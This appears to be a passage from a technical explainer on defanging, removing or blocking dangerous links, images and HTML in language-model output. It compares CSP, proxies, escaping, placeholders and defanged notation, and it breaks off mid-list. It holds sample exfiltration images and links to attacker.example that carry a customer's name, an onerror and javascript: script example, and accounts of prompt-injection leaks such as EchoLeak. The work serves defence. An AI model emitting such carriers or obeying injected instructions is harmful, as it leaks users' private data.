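# Defanging versus blocking: how to neutralise dangerous links, images and HTML in language model output

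## What can displayed model output do, and what do defanging and blocking mean?

A language model's answer reaches an application as plain text. Chat assistants, mail programs and code-hosting sites then turn parts of that text into headings, links, pictures and sometimes working pieces of a web page. Anyone who can influence what the model writes can therefore influence what the reader's software does. Researchers have most often shown this with leaks, in which an image or link in the answer sends private data to a stranger's server. An application that finds such an element can either change it and deliver the rest of the answer, or withhold the answer. "Defanging" is one way of changing the element, and "blocking" usually means withholding the answer, though people in the field use both words loosely.

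### From text to a web request

Chat models mostly write in markdown, a simple notation in which asterisks around a word make it italic and square brackets mark a link. The application receives the answer in chunks while the model is still producing it. In the simplest design described in Chrome for Developers' *Best practices to render streamed LLM responses* (2025), the application adds each new chunk to the earlier ones, converts the whole text into HTML with a markdown parser, and writes that HTML into the page. The browser then handles it like any other part of the page.

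Under CommonMark, a widely used specification of markdown, the image `![foo](train.jpg)` becomes the HTML tag `<img src="train.jpg" alt="foo" />`. The tag contains the image's address rather than the image itself, so the browser requests the image from the server at that address without waiting for the reader to click. The request includes the address's path and query, and whoever runs the server can read both in its log, even if the image doesn't exist.

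A leak therefore requires an address that points to the attacker's server and contains private data, and the model will write one if the attacker can get instructions to it. In prompt injection, a model follows instructions hidden in material it reads. In a July 2025 account of its defences, Microsoft distinguishes direct injection, where the attacker types the instructions, from indirect injection, where the attacker plants them in a web page, email or shared document that someone else asks the model to process. The instructions can be white text on a white background or non-printing characters, and they can be hidden in any file format, including plain text.

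Microsoft describes four channels through which data can leave after a successful injection:

- The model writes an image, in HTML or markdown, whose address points to the attacker's server. The browser sends the data with no action by the user.
- The model writes a clickable link of the same kind, which sends the data once the user clicks.
- The model sends the data through a tool that the application has given it, for example by writing to a public GitHub repository.
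- The model uses a tool as a signal. An outsider who can observe whether the model called the tool learns one bit.

Images and links pass through the display, so an application can deal with them there. Tool calls need other controls, such as asking the user to confirm.

The data can sit in several parts of an address. If the attacker wants the name of a customer, Anna Berg, the model can put it in the query, the path or the subdomain:

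- `https://attacker.example/chart.png?c=Anna%20Berg`
- `https://attacker.example/anna-berg/chart.png`
- `https://anna-berg.attacker.example/chart.png`

The subdomain can leak before the browser connects to the site, because the browser must first look up the hostname, and the attacker may run the name server that answers. Microsoft also mentions base64, a common encoding that turns the customer's name into `QW5uYSBCZXJn`. A filter that searches outgoing addresses for customer names would miss it.

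Microsoft calls the deterministic detection of indirect injection an open research challenge. It designs its products on the assumption that some injections will succeed, and aims to prevent those from doing damage. A rule about what the display may load does not depend on catching the injection first, because it applies however the model came to write the address.

### Carriers

A carrier is an element of the output that can cause an effect when software displays it or someone uses it. The usual ones look like this in the text that the model writes:

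| Carrier | Notation | Effect | Click needed? |
|---|---|---|---|
| Inline image | `![chart](https://attacker.example/a.png)` | The browser requests the address | No |
| Reference-style image | `![chart][q3]`, with `[q3]: https://attacker.example/a.png` elsewhere | The same | No |
| Inline link | `[report](https://attacker.example/r)` | The browser opens the address | Yes |
| Reference-style link | `[report][q3]`, with the address elsewhere | The same | Yes |
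| Automatic link | `<https://attacker.example/r>` | The same | Yes |
| Raw HTML | `<img src="https://attacker.example/a.png">`, or any other tag | Depends on the tag | Depends on the tag |
| Mention or command | `@name` in a comment | The platform notifies someone or carries out the command | No |

Reference-style forms are easy to overlook. The address can be far from the visible text, labels are case-insensitive, and `[q3]` alone makes a link if the document defines that label anywhere. A filter that looks for square brackets followed directly by an address in parentheses misses them. EchoLeak, a 2025 attack on Microsoft 365 Copilot, used this gap.

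What counts as a carrier also depends on the renderer, the software that turns the notation into what the user sees. Under CommonMark, a bare address with no brackets around it stays ordinary text. Many systems make it clickable anyway (Grimminck, 2026, *Safe and Reversible Sharing of Malicious URLs and Indicators*). Renderers differ even more in how they handle raw HTML. CommonMark passes anything that looks like a tag through unescaped, including custom tags, but many applications turn that off.

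Mentions and commands take effect without a browser. When a model posts a comment on a code-hosting site, `@name` notifies a real person. A workflow script in a Libre-Chip repository neutralises mentions "to prevent unintended notifications", according to a comment in the code.

The column about clicks separates zero-click carriers, which act as soon as software displays them, from one-click carriers, which act only when the user clicks. In *Trust No AI*, Rehberger (2024) names eleven products in which he had found and reported the zero-click image leak, including ChatGPT, Claude, Google Bard and GitHub Copilot Chat. He considers it one of the most common security flaws in applications built on language models. Several vendors have since shipped fixes.

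Links are less dangerous because the reader has to click them, but this is weaker protection than it seems. Readers decide whether to click based on the link's visible text, which the model chooses separately from the address. Rehberger reports an attack on Microsoft 365 Copilot, discovered in February 2024, that began with a phishing email. The injected instructions made Copilot fetch sensitive information from the user's inbox and put it in a clickable link as invisible characters. Microsoft fixed the flaw that July. Amazon responded to a leak in its Q for Business assistant by no longer rendering links.

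A one-click carrier can become a zero-click one outside the chat window. Slack, Discord and Teams automatically fetch links to show previews, and Rehberger notes that the fetch delivers any data the address contains. Some mail systems also fetch links automatically to scan for malware.

### Leaks, scripts and deception

Besides exfiltration, the sending of private data to an outsider, a carrier can run a script in the reader's browser. Chrome for Developers gives the example of an image tag with an invalid address and an `onerror` attribute that contains code. When the image fails to load, the browser runs the code. According to Rehberger, a flaw of this kind in DeepSeek's service allowed an attacker to take over a user's account. A carrier can also deceive the reader. In one of Rehberger's demonstrations against Google's Gemini, the answer contained a link that connected the victim to a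 scammer in a video call.

*Shifting from Injection to Interaction* (Singh, Abuadbba and colleagues, 2026) separates these harms when it maps language model risks to the Common Weakness Enumeration (CWE), a catalogue of software flaws that the American non-profit MITRE maintains. It places data exfiltration under CWE-200 (exposure of sensitive information) and output that leads to execution under CWE-116 (improper encoding or escaping). It lists no equivalent entry for content manipulation and social engineering, because these harms come from what the model generates rather than from a classical programming error.

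A defence against one of these harms can leave another untouched. The markdown renderer of TanStack, a collection of open-source web libraries, escapes raw HTML and removes executable addresses by default. According to its documentation, the policy for outbound links and remote images is left to the application. A developer who keeps the defaults and adds no policy is protected against scripts but not against the image leak.

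Model output can deceive a user without links, images or HTML. Rehberger got the writing assistant in Google Docs to produce a scam message that asked the user to call a phone number. A renderer treats the number as plain text, so disarming links and images would not have changed the message.

### An example answer

Suppose that a sales manager asks an assistant to summarise a quarterly report. Someone has hidden instructions in the report, and the assistant also has access to customer records. It writes the following markdown:

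```
Renewals rose to 84 per cent in the third quarter, two points
more than in the second. [Full report](https://reports.example/q3)

![Renewals](https://img.attacker.example/chart.png?c=Anna%20Berg)

To show the company logo on your own page, paste this:

`<img src="https://assets.example/logo.png" alt="Logo">`
```

All the addresses use `.example`, an ending that nobody can register. The link to the full report is useful because the manager may want to check the figure against it. The image is an attack that sends a customer's name to `img.attacker.example` as soon as the application displays it. The last line contains an `img` tag, but the backticks around it mark it as code, so a correct renderer shows the tag as text and requests nothing. A crude filter may treat this tag as a second image, or flag all three addresses as suspicious.

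### What the words mean

Neutralising a carrier means stopping it from having its effect. Defanging, removal and blocking all do this, but they differ in what the manager receives.

Defanging rewrites a carrier so that it no longer works but a reader can still see what it was. The practice comes from security analysts, who need to share the addresses of malicious sites without anyone opening them by accident. Its familiar form is `hxxps://example[.]com`. Grimminck's proposal, which is not an internet standard, instead puts brackets around the scheme and the dots of the host. It advises against `hxxp` in new text because variant spellings such as `h**p` defeat automatic parsing. The proposal uses the term "obfuscating". An earlier version, *A Standard for Safe and Reversible Sharing of Malicious URLs and Indicators* (Grimminck, 2025), equated this with what people had called defanging. Restoring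 the working address is called refanging.

Under Grimminck's rule, the injected image would appear as its defanged address, `[https]://img[.]attacker[.]example/chart.png?c=Anna%20Berg`, and the browser would request nothing. The manager could see that something odd had happened and which server was involved. The customer's name would still be visible, because the rule doesn't change ordinary text in the path and query.

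Removal deletes the carrier, sometimes leaving a placeholder such as "image removed", and delivers the rest of the output. The manager still gets the summary, the source link and the code sample. The term "rewriting" covers defanging, removal and any other treatment that changes a carrier but still delivers the output.

Blocking rejects the whole output, or the whole operation that would use it. The manager gets an error message instead of the summary, and loses a correct figure, a good link and a harmless line of code along with the image.

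The broad sense of neutralisation agrees with MITRE's *CWE Glossary*, which defines "neutralization" as "ensuring that input or output has certain security properties before it is used". This definition doesn't depend on the mechanism, and MITRE's list of mechanisms includes filtering, encoding and escaping, which change the data, as well as validation, which can end in a refusal. In the glossary's entry for "enforce", a program that should accept only letters and digits can either delete all other characters or reject the input entirely. MITRE's term is wider than the neutralisation of carriers in model output because it covers any data that a program handles, such as database queries. MITRE discourages "sanitization" in the names and descriptions of weaknesses because the industry gives it too many meanings, but "sanitiser" is still the usual name for software that parses HTML or markdown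 and removes or changes what its rules do not permit.

Everyday use of "block" is no more consistent. Microsoft writes that it took steps to "deterministically block" the leak through markdown images, and later to block other techniques such as certain untrusted links. These steps block a channel, and the user may still receive the answer. In the same account, Microsoft also writes that an application may "block the prompt completely", which is blocking in the strict sense. A product notice that a link "was blocked" usually means the link was removed.

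One system can both rewrite and block model output. In GitHub Agentic Workflows, a model proposes operations, such as opening an issue or posting a comment, and a separate job with write permission carries them out. GitHub's *Safe Outputs MCP Gateway Specification* (2026) requires that job to remove malicious addresses and injected commands from the text while preserving legitimate content. The job rejects any operation that is malformed or exceeds a configured limit.

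Chrome for Developers, by contrast, recommends something close to pure blocking. The application runs a sanitiser over all the text received so far, because dangerous code can be split across two chunks, and stops rendering as soon as the sanitiser removes anything. It doesn't show the cleaned version because that is no longer the model's original output. The user has already seen the beginning of a streamed answer by then, so the application blocks only the rest. The sample code also runs the sanitiser before the markdown parser converts the text. An HTML sanitiser treats a markdown image as plain text, so the manager's answer would probably pass the check with the attacker's image intact.

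## In what ways can a link, image or HTML tag be made harmless?

An application can act on a carrier when it converts the markdown into HTML, when the browser is about to load something, or when the reader clicks. The mildest methods leave the answer as the model wrote it and add a check before the request. The strictest delete the carrier. With no defence at all, a parser that follows CommonMark turns the sales manager's answer into this HTML:

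```html
<p>Renewals rose to 84 per cent in the third quarter, two points
more than in the second. <a href="https://reports.example/q3">Full report</a></p>
<p><img src="https://img.attacker.example/chart.png?c=Anna%20Berg" alt="Renewals" /></p>
<p>To show the company logo on your own page, paste this:</p>
<p><code>&lt;img src=&quot;https://assets.example/logo.png&quot; alt=&quot;Logo&quot;&gt;</code></p>
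```

The link and the chart work, but the logo tag does nothing because the parser has turned its angle brackets into `&lt;` and `&gt;`. Below, the assistant runs on a site called `app.example`.

### Checks before a link opens or an image loads

A confirmation step leaves the link in place but requires the user to confirm before it opens. *Link Safety* describes this step in Streamdown, a library that displays markdown from language models. When the manager clicks "Full report", a dialog shows `https://reports.example/q3` in full, with the buttons "Copy link" and "Open link". Pressing Escape or clicking outside the dialog closes it without opening the link. The developer can exempt trusted sites by supplying a function that checks the address, consulting a server if necessary, and determines whether the dialog appears.

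The dialog shows the reader the real address, which the link text can hide. If the attacker had used a link for the leak, the manager could have read `?c=Anna%20Berg` before opening it. The same name in base64 would probably have looked like an ordinary tracking code. The dialog doesn't protect against the chart, because images load without a click.

A redirect page changes the address so that the click goes to the application's own site first:

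```html
<a href="https://app.example/leaving?to=https%3A%2F%2Freports.example%2Fq3">Full report</a>
```

The manager sees the same link as before. After the click, the server at `app.example` reads the original address from the `to` parameter. It can compare the address with a list of malicious sites, show a warning, or forward the browser at once. Checking at the click can catch a site that nobody knew to be malicious when the model wrote the answer. The link also keeps working in an email or an exported document, which would lack the code for a confirmation dialog.

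The redirect page makes the address harder to read, since a manager who hovers over the link sees `app.example` first. The page should forward only addresses that the application itself put into links, which it can check if, for example, the application signs each one. Otherwise anyone can use the page to disguise a link to a malicious site as a link to `app.example`.

An image proxy does something similar for pictures. Streamdown's *Security* includes a short function that puts the address of a proxy in front of every image address. For the chart, with a proxy on `app.example`, the result would be:

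```html
<img src="https://app.example/proxy?url=https%3A%2F%2Fimg.attacker.example%2Fchart.png%3Fc%3DAnna%2520Berg" alt="Renewals">
```

(The `%20` in the name becomes `%2520` because the function also encodes the percent sign.) The browser now contacts only `app.example`. The proxy fetches the picture from the original server and passes it on, so the attacker sees the proxy's network address instead of the manager's and receives none of the manager's cookies.

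A proxy helps against tracking, but it doesn't by itself stop the leak. If it fetches the original address, it sends `?c=Anna%20Berg` to the attacker just as the browser would. The proxy must also refuse unknown hosts, which Streamdown's sample function leaves to the developer.

### Restrictions in the browser

A Content Security Policy (CSP) is a set of rules that a website sends to the browser along with the page. It can be a single line in the server's response:

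```
Content-Security-Policy: img-src 'self' https://assets.example
```

This line permits images from the application's own site and from `assets.example`. The browser compares the chart's address with the list, finds no match and sends no request. The HTML is unchanged and still includes the customer's name in the `src` attribute. The manager sees a broken-image symbol, usually with the alternative text "Renewals".

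The browser checks the request itself, so the same rule applies to an inline image, a reference-style image and a raw `img` tag, and a CSP avoids the gap that EchoLeak used. A `script-src` rule that doesn't permit inline code would also stop the `onerror` script from the earlier example. But `img-src` doesn't restrict links, so the manager can still open the report and could also open a link with a customer's name in it. The policy also covers the whole page, so the list has to include every server from which the application loads its own pictures.

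A sandboxed frame is a page within the page, to which the browser gives fewer rights. nr-llm's *Rendering LLM Markdown server-side safely* describes how nr-llm, an extension for the content management system TYPO3, uses such a frame to preview HTML that a model has written. An application could put the chart in one like this:

```html
<iframe sandbox="" srcdoc="<img src='https://img.attacker.example/chart.png?c=Anna%20Berg' alt='Renewals'>"></iframe>
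```

The empty `sandbox` value turns on every restriction, so scripts in the frame don't run, forms don't submit, and the framed document can't access the page around it. In nr-llm's words, the attribute "confines the document instead of sanitizing it". This suits cases where the user asked for a web page and wants to see it, since no markdown setting would make a whole page safe to insert directly.

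The sandbox doesn't block images, so the browser draws the chart inside the frame and sends the name to the attacker. The frame protects the application from the document, but it doesn't protect the data already in the document. A CSP on the surrounding page can prevent this leak, because a `srcdoc` frame inherits that page's policy.

### Showing the markup as text

Escaping replaces the characters that have a special meaning in HTML with codes that the browser draws as ordinary characters. If the model had written the chart as a raw HTML tag, escaping would have produced this:

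```html
&lt;img src=&quot;https://img.attacker.example/chart.png?c=Anna%20Berg&quot; alt=&quot;Renewals&quot;&gt;
```

The manager would have seen the tag as text, and the browser would have requested nothing. But the model wrote the chart in markdown, and an application that escapes raw HTML and then renders the markdown still creates a working image. According to Streamdown, the same is true of its setting that turns HTML off.

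To stop the chart by escaping, the application has to escape the entire answer and leave the markdown unrendered. The manager would then see the square brackets, the exclamation mark and both addresses in full. nr-llm escapes answers this way in its own administration screens and recommends it as a fallback for websites that convert markdown on the server. If the converter fails, the page shows the escaped source text, so an answer designed to crash the converter can't take the page down or put unescaped text on it.

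If the application escapes the answer before rendering the markdown, the logo sample breaks. CommonMark treats codes such as `&lt;` inside backticks as literal text, so the parser escapes the sample a second time. The manager then sees `&lt;img src=` instead of `<img src=` and copies code that doesn't work.

Escaping also fails to neutralise some dangerous addresses. `javascript:alert(1)` contains none of the characters that escaping changes, so it stays unchanged in a link's `href` attribute and runs when someone clicks the link. nr-llm warns about this for source links that a page template builds separately from the model's text, and advises developers to check those addresses on the server.

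Wrapping the output in a code block reaches nearly the same result within markdown. The application puts a line of backticks, called a fence, before and after the answer. The parser then treats everything in between as code:

```html
<pre><code>Renewals rose to 84 per cent in the third quarter, two points
more than in the second. [Full report](https://reports.example/q3)

![Renewals](https://img.attacker.example/chart.png?c=Anna%20Berg)
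...
</code></pre>
```

The code fence around the answer has to be longer than any run of backticks inside it. If the application uses three backticks and the answer contains a line of three, that line closes the block and the rest is rendered as markdown. Syntax highlighters, which colour the words in a code sample, can also undo the protection. According to TanStack's *Security*, a highlighter returns HTML that the renderer inserts into the `<code>` element without further escaping, so a highlighter that fails to escape the sample can turn it back into a working tag.

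### Defanged notation

Escaped text and code blocks still contain working addresses. A browser does not act on them, but chat programs that fetch links for previews may. Defanging changes the address itself, so software no longer recognises it as an address.

The security analysts who began the practice exchange "indicators of compromise", which are the web, network and email addresses that malware or its operators use. They share these in emails, tickets, chat channels and PDF reports, and much of the software involved turns anything that looks like an address into a link. According to Grimminck, opening such a link by accident can install malware, reveal the analyst's network address and employer, or alert the attackers that someone is investigating them.

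Analysts therefore began to write `hxxp` for `http` and to put brackets around the dots. Hugo Salgado of NIC Chile, which runs the `.cl` domain, tried to have `hxxp` officially recorded. In *Registration of "hxxp" URI scheme*, a message to an Internet Engineering Task Force (IETF) mailing list, he wrote that it had been a de facto standard in the security community for many years. Salgado (2017), in *The "hxxp" and "hxxps" URI Schemes*, wrote that it was meant for human readers only, and was meant to keep browsers from loading a dangerous address and programs from making it clickable.

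John Levine questioned the proposal in a message that Mark Nottingham quoted on the list. He wrote that the whole point of `hxxp` was "to prevent interoperation", so he didn't see what a permanent registration would solve, and he suggested a provisional one. The Internet Assigned Numbers Authority (IANA), which keeps the register of address schemes, gave `hxxp` provisional status in an entry dated 9 May 2017, which forbids applications from using `hxxp` addresses (IANA, 2017). Salgado's draft expired that November.

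Grimminck's draft is a more ambitious attempt, because it tries to make the notation readable for machines as well. The latest version, of September 2026, fixes a single form and the order of the steps:

1. Put brackets around the scheme, so that `https` becomes `[https]`.
2. Put brackets around the `@` sign in an email address or before a host name.
3. Put brackets around the dots in the host.
4. Search the path, the query and the fragment (the part after `#`) for further addresses, and treat those in the same way.

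Under the older habit and the new rule, the chart's address looks like this:

```
hxxps://img[.]attacker[.]example/chart.png?c=Anna%20Berg
[https]://img[.]attacker[.]example/chart.png?c=Anna%20Berg
```

`hxxps` has the form of a valid scheme, which is why Salgado wanted to reserve it. A scheme can't begin with a square bracket, so no program should mistake `[https]` for one. Applying the rule a second time changes nothing, which helps when two programs in a row defang the same text. Grimminck also requires both the scheme and the dots to change. `https://img[.]attacker[.]example` has an intact scheme, so some software may make it clickable.

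The fourth step applies to addresses inside other addresses, such as the destination in a redirect link. `https://app.example/leaving?to=https://reports.example/q3` becomes `[https]://app[.]example/leaving?to=[https]://reports[.]example/q3`. The rule matches only literal text, so it doesn't change an inner address whose colon and slashes are encoded as `%3A%2F%2F`.

In an IETF review of the draft, *Early Review of draft-grimminck-safe-ioc-sharing-10*, Bray (2026) found it ready apart from small corrections. He was a little surprised that security staff needed such a thing, and suggested a warning against editing defanged text by hand because it would be easy to break.

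The drafts were written for analysts' reports, and model output adds a complication, because markdown and HTML have places where an address is not visible. An application that merely changes the address inside the `img` tag to `hxxps://...` gives the manager a broken image and no explanation. The bracketed form works even less well there. It doesn't begin with a valid scheme, so the browser takes it for a path on the current site and requests it from `app.example`. The defanged address belongs in the visible text:

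```html
<p>Renewals: [https]://img[.]attacker[.]example/chart.png?c=Anna%20Berg</p>
```

The application should insert this text after the markdown parser has run, because `[https]` in markdown source becomes a link if the answer defines a label with that name elsewhere. An attacker who can influence the answer can add that definition.

HTML also has a form of defanging that keeps the address out of the reader's sight. Cardwell (2026), in *htmlpolicy*, offers a rule that renames an attribute. Applied to the chart's `src`, it gives:

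```html
<img htmlpolicy-defanged-src="https://img.attacker.example/chart.png?c=Anna%20Berg" alt="Renewals">
```

Browsers ignore attributes they don't recognise, so the tag no longer loads anything. The manager sees the word "Renewals" at most, while a developer can find the address in the page's source. *htmlpolicy* illustrates the technique well but is a poor authority on security. It had not reached version 1.0 in June 2026, and according to its documentation Cardwell built it entirely by "vibe coding" with the AI tool Claude Code.

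### Placeholders, bare text and removal

The remaining methods remove the link, image or tag and differ in what they leave in its place. A developer can compare them in *harden-react-markdown*, which adds a filter to react-markdown, a component that displays markdown in web applications. A related library, *rehype-harden*, does the same for other programs that process HTML with the rehype toolkit. In both, the developer lists the beginnings of permitted addresses, separately for links and images. A setting called a block policy controls what, if anything, replaces a link or image whose address doesn't match the list.

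If neither `reports.example` nor `img.attacker.example` is on the list, the manager sees the following:

| Policy | In place of the link | In place of the image |
|---|---|---|
| `indicator` (the default) | Full report [blocked] | [Image blocked: Renewals] |
| `text-only` | Full report | Renewals |
| `remove` | Nothing | Nothing |

The `indicator` policy keeps more than the table suggests. The library puts the address of a refused link into a `title` attribute, so the HTML looks roughly like this:

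```html
<span title="https://reports.example/q3">Full report [blocked]</span>
```

A desktop browser shows the content of `title` when the pointer rests on the words, so a manager at a desk can see where the link led and copy the address by hand if it looks legitimate. On a phone, the address is still in the page, but the manager usually can't get to it. `indicator` therefore comes close to defanging links, but it simply removes images and leaves a placeholder. The documentation mentions only the alternative text for images, and the manager learns that an image is missing but not which server it would have contacted.

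Streamdown uses *rehype-harden*, and Streamdown's documentation is inconsistent about what happens to a refused link. According to one sentence, the link is rewritten to point to the application's own site, but in the example that follows, it becomes `[blocked]`. The example matches *rehype-harden*'s own documentation.

A developer can set the policies for links and images separately, for example `text-only` for links and `remove` for images. With `text-only` for both, the manager sees the paragraph about renewals, then the words "Full report", then the word "Renewals" on its own line, with no sign that there was ever a link or an image. An image without alternative text disappears completely. TanStack offers the same option through a function that examines each address. If the function returns `null`, the renderer drops the link or image and keeps its label. Returning an empty string is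 a mistake, because an image then stays in the page with an empty address.

Full removal deletes the label too. Under `remove`, the answer reads:

```
Renewals rose to 84 per cent in the third quarter, two points
more than in the second.

To show the company logo on your own page, paste this:

<img src="https://assets.example/logo.png" alt="Logo">
```

The library keeps the logo sample because it works on the parsed document, where the sample is code, not an image. A filter that searched the raw text for `<img` might have deleted the sample and left the manager with instructions to paste code that was no longer there.

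Some tools remove carriers without looking at the address. unified's *remark-unlink* removes every link, image, reference and definition from a markdown document. Its developers meant it for paper, manual pages and some e-readers, where links don't work. The converter settings that nr-llm recommends strip any raw HTML the model wrote, and Streamdown has an option to ignore it. Neither setting removes images written in markdown, so the chart would still load.

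The table shows what each method does to the sales manager's answer when the application uses no other defence. The code block row and the rows below it cover the case where the application applies the method to both the link and the chart.

| Method | What the manager sees | Can a request still leave the browser? |
|---|---|---|
| Confirmation step | The answer unchanged, and a dialog with the full address after a click on the link | Yes: the chart loads at once, the link after confirmation |
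| Redirect page | The answer unchanged, and possibly a warning page after a click | Yes: the chart loads at once, and a click goes to `app.example` first |
| Image proxy | The answer with the chart | Yes: to the proxy, which may pass the name on, and to the link's site after a click |
| CSP with an image rule | A broken image, and a working link | Not for the chart, but the link still opens |
| Sandboxed frame | The answer inside a frame, with the chart | Yes: the chart loads at once |
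| Escaping raw HTML only | The answer unchanged, because the chart is in markdown | Yes: the chart loads at once |
| Escaping the whole answer | The markdown source, with both addresses | No, unless other software makes the addresses clickable |
| Code block | The markdown source in a fixed-width font | No, if the fence is long enough |
| Defanged notation | Both addresses, in a form that doesn't open | No |
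| Renamed attribute | The labels at most, with the addresses in the page's source | No |
| Placeholder (`indicator`) | "Full report [blocked]" and "[Image blocked: Renewals]" | No |
| Text only | "Full report" and "Renewals" as ordinary words | No |
| Full removal | No trace of the link or the chart | No |

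## What information does each kind of rewriting lose?

Rewriting a carrier usually removes more than the danger. The link and the chart in the sales manager's answer hold up to five things between them:

- a destination, which is the address
- a label, which is the link text or the image's alternative text
- a function, since the link opens a page after a click and the chart loads by itself
- a role as a citation, because the link tells the manager where the 84 per cent came from
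- value as evidence, because the chart's address shows that someone tried to take a customer's name, and which server was waiting for it

The table shows which of these still reach the manager if the defanged version prints the label and the full address, the placeholder prints the label and a marker but no address, and nobody keeps a copy of the original.

| | Defanging | Placeholder | Text only | Removal | Blocking |
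|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Destination | Kept | Lost | Lost | Lost | Lost |
| Label | Kept | Kept | Kept | Lost | Lost |
| Function | Lost | Lost | Lost | Lost | Lost |
| Role as a citation | Mostly kept: the reader can look up the address | Weakened: the reader knows that a source existed | Kept only if the label names the source | Lost, but the claim remains | Lost together with the claim |
| Evidence of an attack | Kept | The reader knows that something is missing | Lost | Lost | The reader knows that something went wrong |

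When rewriting removes a link's address and keeps only its label, a reader can find the source only if the label identifies it. "Q3 renewals report, page 4" would be enough, but "Full report" is little help, and "here" or "1" is useless.

Rewriting an image loses more information than rewriting a link, because an image's content is the picture itself. If the chart had been genuine, the manager would have lost every figure in it, and the word "Renewals" would not have replaced them. Only defanging would have let the manager recover the chart, by opening the address by hand.

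Blocking loses the most information, but it removes claims along with their sources. Removing only the link leaves the manager with the claim that renewals rose to 84 per cent and no source to check it against.

Products don't always fit one category. By default, *harden-react-markdown* keeps a blocked link's address in a tooltip but drops a blocked image's address. Google's *Mitigating prompt injection attacks with a layered defense strategy* (2025) shows an email summary in which Gemini has replaced an unsafe address with the words "suspicious link removed". The reader learns that Google removed a link it distrusted, but not where the link led.

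### When a program can undo the rewriting

A rewriting is reversible if a program can recover the original answer from the rewritten text alone. This is possible exactly when no two different answers produce the same rewritten text. If two answers did, the program could not determine which one was the original.

Placeholders discard the image's address. Every blocked image labelled "Renewals" becomes `[Image blocked: Renewals]`, whether its address belonged to an attacker or to the company's own chart server.

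Defanging keeps the address, but it can still produce collisions. Suppose the quarterly report also warns about fake invoices, and the assistant copies the warning:

```
Our invoices link to https://invoices.example
The fake ones link to hxxps://invoices-pay.example
```

Whoever wrote the warning had already defanged the fake address. An application that defangs by changing `https` to `hxxps` then delivers this:

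```
Our invoices link to hxxps://invoices.example
The fake ones link to hxxps://invoices-pay.example
```

Defanging loses the distinction between addresses that worked and addresses that were already defanged. If a model's answer contains one working address and the already defanged address of a phishing site, defanging it produces the same text as an answer with two working addresses. A program that refangs this text can't tell which address originally worked. If it restores both, it creates a working phishing link that wasn't in the model's answer.

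If the text already contains an `hxxps` link, the application can leave it alone and mark the links it defangs differently, as in `[https]://invoices[.]example`. A program that restores only the bracketed form then recovers the original text. However, Grimminck's draft recommends that restoring programs recognise `hxxps` too. That helps an analyst extract every address from a report, but here it would again activate both links.

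The bracketed form also has a collision. In the draft's test cases, the inputs `https://bad.example` and `[https]://bad[.]example` both give `[https]://bad[.]example`. This happens with any defanging rule that changes nothing when applied a second time. Such a rule satisfies *f*(*f*(*x*)) = *f*(*x*), so whenever it changes a text *x*, the different inputs *x* and *f*(*x*) give the same output. The rule therefore cannot be reversible for every text.

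The draft's claim of reversibility therefore makes sense only for addresses that are still live, and even then it has exceptions. `http://evil%2eexample`, in which `%2e` stands for a dot, is restored as `http://evil.example`. The two addresses are equivalent, but an investigator might have wanted to see the odd spelling because it could be an attempt to get past a filter. If a path originally contained `[.]`, it is restored with a plain dot instead. Grimminck warns that an attacker who controls the path can use this to make a reported address turn into a different one when it is restored.

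By contrast, a program can always undo HTML escaping, because escaping turns every `&` into `&amp;`. A text that already contained `&lt;` becomes `&amp;lt;` and stays distinct from a text that contained `<`. But escaping twice changes the text twice, which is how the logo sample can end up as code that doesn't work.

Markers written in ordinary words can collide as well. Imagine that the assistant lists the sales team's projects, and that one line of its answer is either of these:

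```
New web shop [blocked]
[New web shop](https://shop.example)
```

A manager who reads "New web shop [blocked]" can't tell which of two things happened. If the model wrote "[blocked]" itself, without a link, the project is waiting for someone. If the model wrote "New web shop" as a link, *harden-react-markdown* refused the address and added "[blocked]". Only the refused link has a tooltip in the HTML, and the tooltip is lost when the manager copies the words into a plain-text email. An attacker could also fake a security notice by making the model write "suspicious link removed".

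The application can avoid this by drawing the marker as an icon or a coloured box that the model cannot produce. In plain text, it can add a random code to the marker after the model has finished, for example `[link removed 7f3a]`, and check that the answer doesn't already contain that code. The marker then reliably shows that the application removed something, but not what it removed.

### Keeping the original

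If the application saves the model's original text, along with the place and reason for each change, a program can look up the original instead of reconstructing it. This solves the remaining problem even after full removal or blocking, when the manager's screen shows nothing of the removed content.

GitHub's *Under the hood* (2026) lists "log everything" among the four security principles behind Agentic Workflows. The model's original answer contains evidence that an investigator couldn't get from a placeholder on the manager's screen. The chart's address alone shows the attacker's server, the data it was meant to receive, and how the model encoded that data. The rest of the answer helps to show which document carried the hidden instructions.

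But the log now contains the customer's name. GitHub's output sanitisation includes removing secrets, so a log of the text before that step could contain them. Defanging the log doesn't hide this information. One of Grimminck's test cases turns `http://user:pass@attacker.example` into `[http]://user:pass[@]attacker[.]example`, which leaves the password readable, and the draft advises against sharing credentials even in this form. Developers who keep the originals therefore have to restrict who can read them and decide when to delete them.

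The program that displays the log also has to show the answer as plain text. If it rendered the markdown, the investigator's browser would load the chart and complete the leak. The draft has a similar rule for refanging, under which a program may restore an address only where no software will open it or turn it into a link.

### Damage to code samples

The logo sample is a correct answer to a question about HTML, and its address is part of what makes it correct. A filter that defangs every address in the raw markdown changes it to this:

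```html
<img src="[https]://assets[.]example/logo.png" alt="Logo">
```

If the manager pastes this into a page, the logo doesn't appear. In some ways this is worse than deleting the sample, because the manager may not notice the change and may blame the assistant or the web server. *harden-react-markdown* avoids the problem by filtering the parsed document.

Refanging can damage code too. Grimminck gives the example of a regular expression, a pattern that programs use to search text. The pattern `[0-9]+[.][0-9]+` finds decimal numbers such as 84.2, because `[.]` matches only a literal dot. A program that replaces every `[.]` with `.` turns it into `[0-9]+.[0-9]+`. A bare dot matches any character, so the code still runs but now also accepts 84x2 and the whole number 842. The draft therefore recommends that programs restore only complete addresses.

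Leaving all code unchanged is also risky. The hidden instructions could have put the attacker's address into the logo sample, and the manager would then have pasted code that contacts the attacker's server into a real page. An application could warn the manager without breaking correct code by listing the servers that a sample contacts below it.

### Silent removal and the missing source

When a filter removes a link entirely and leaves no marker, the manager can't tell whether the model gave no source or the filter deleted a good one. If the model gave no source, the manager has reason to doubt the figure and should ask the assistant for evidence. If the filter deleted a good source, the missing link is no reason to doubt the figure, and someone should add `reports.example` to the allowlist.

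How much this matters depends on whether people use the links in AI answers. Warren, Eser and colleagues (2026), in *When Should I Trust This?*, surveyed 1,000 American chatbot users in May 2025, who said that reviewing the chatbot's sources was among their most common ways of checking an answer. The share was lower in a British Ipsos study reported by Reeves (2026), in *Unreliable AI answers are 'good enough' for most users of platforms*, where about a quarter of ChatGPT users said they opened its links.

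Observed behaviour is mostly lower still:

- Ding, Facciani and colleagues (2025), in *Citations and Trust in LLM Generated Answers*, let participants ask a chatbot ten questions of their own. Participants checked the citations, which showed their address under the mouse pointer, in 193 of 1,976 answers that had any (9.77 per cent).
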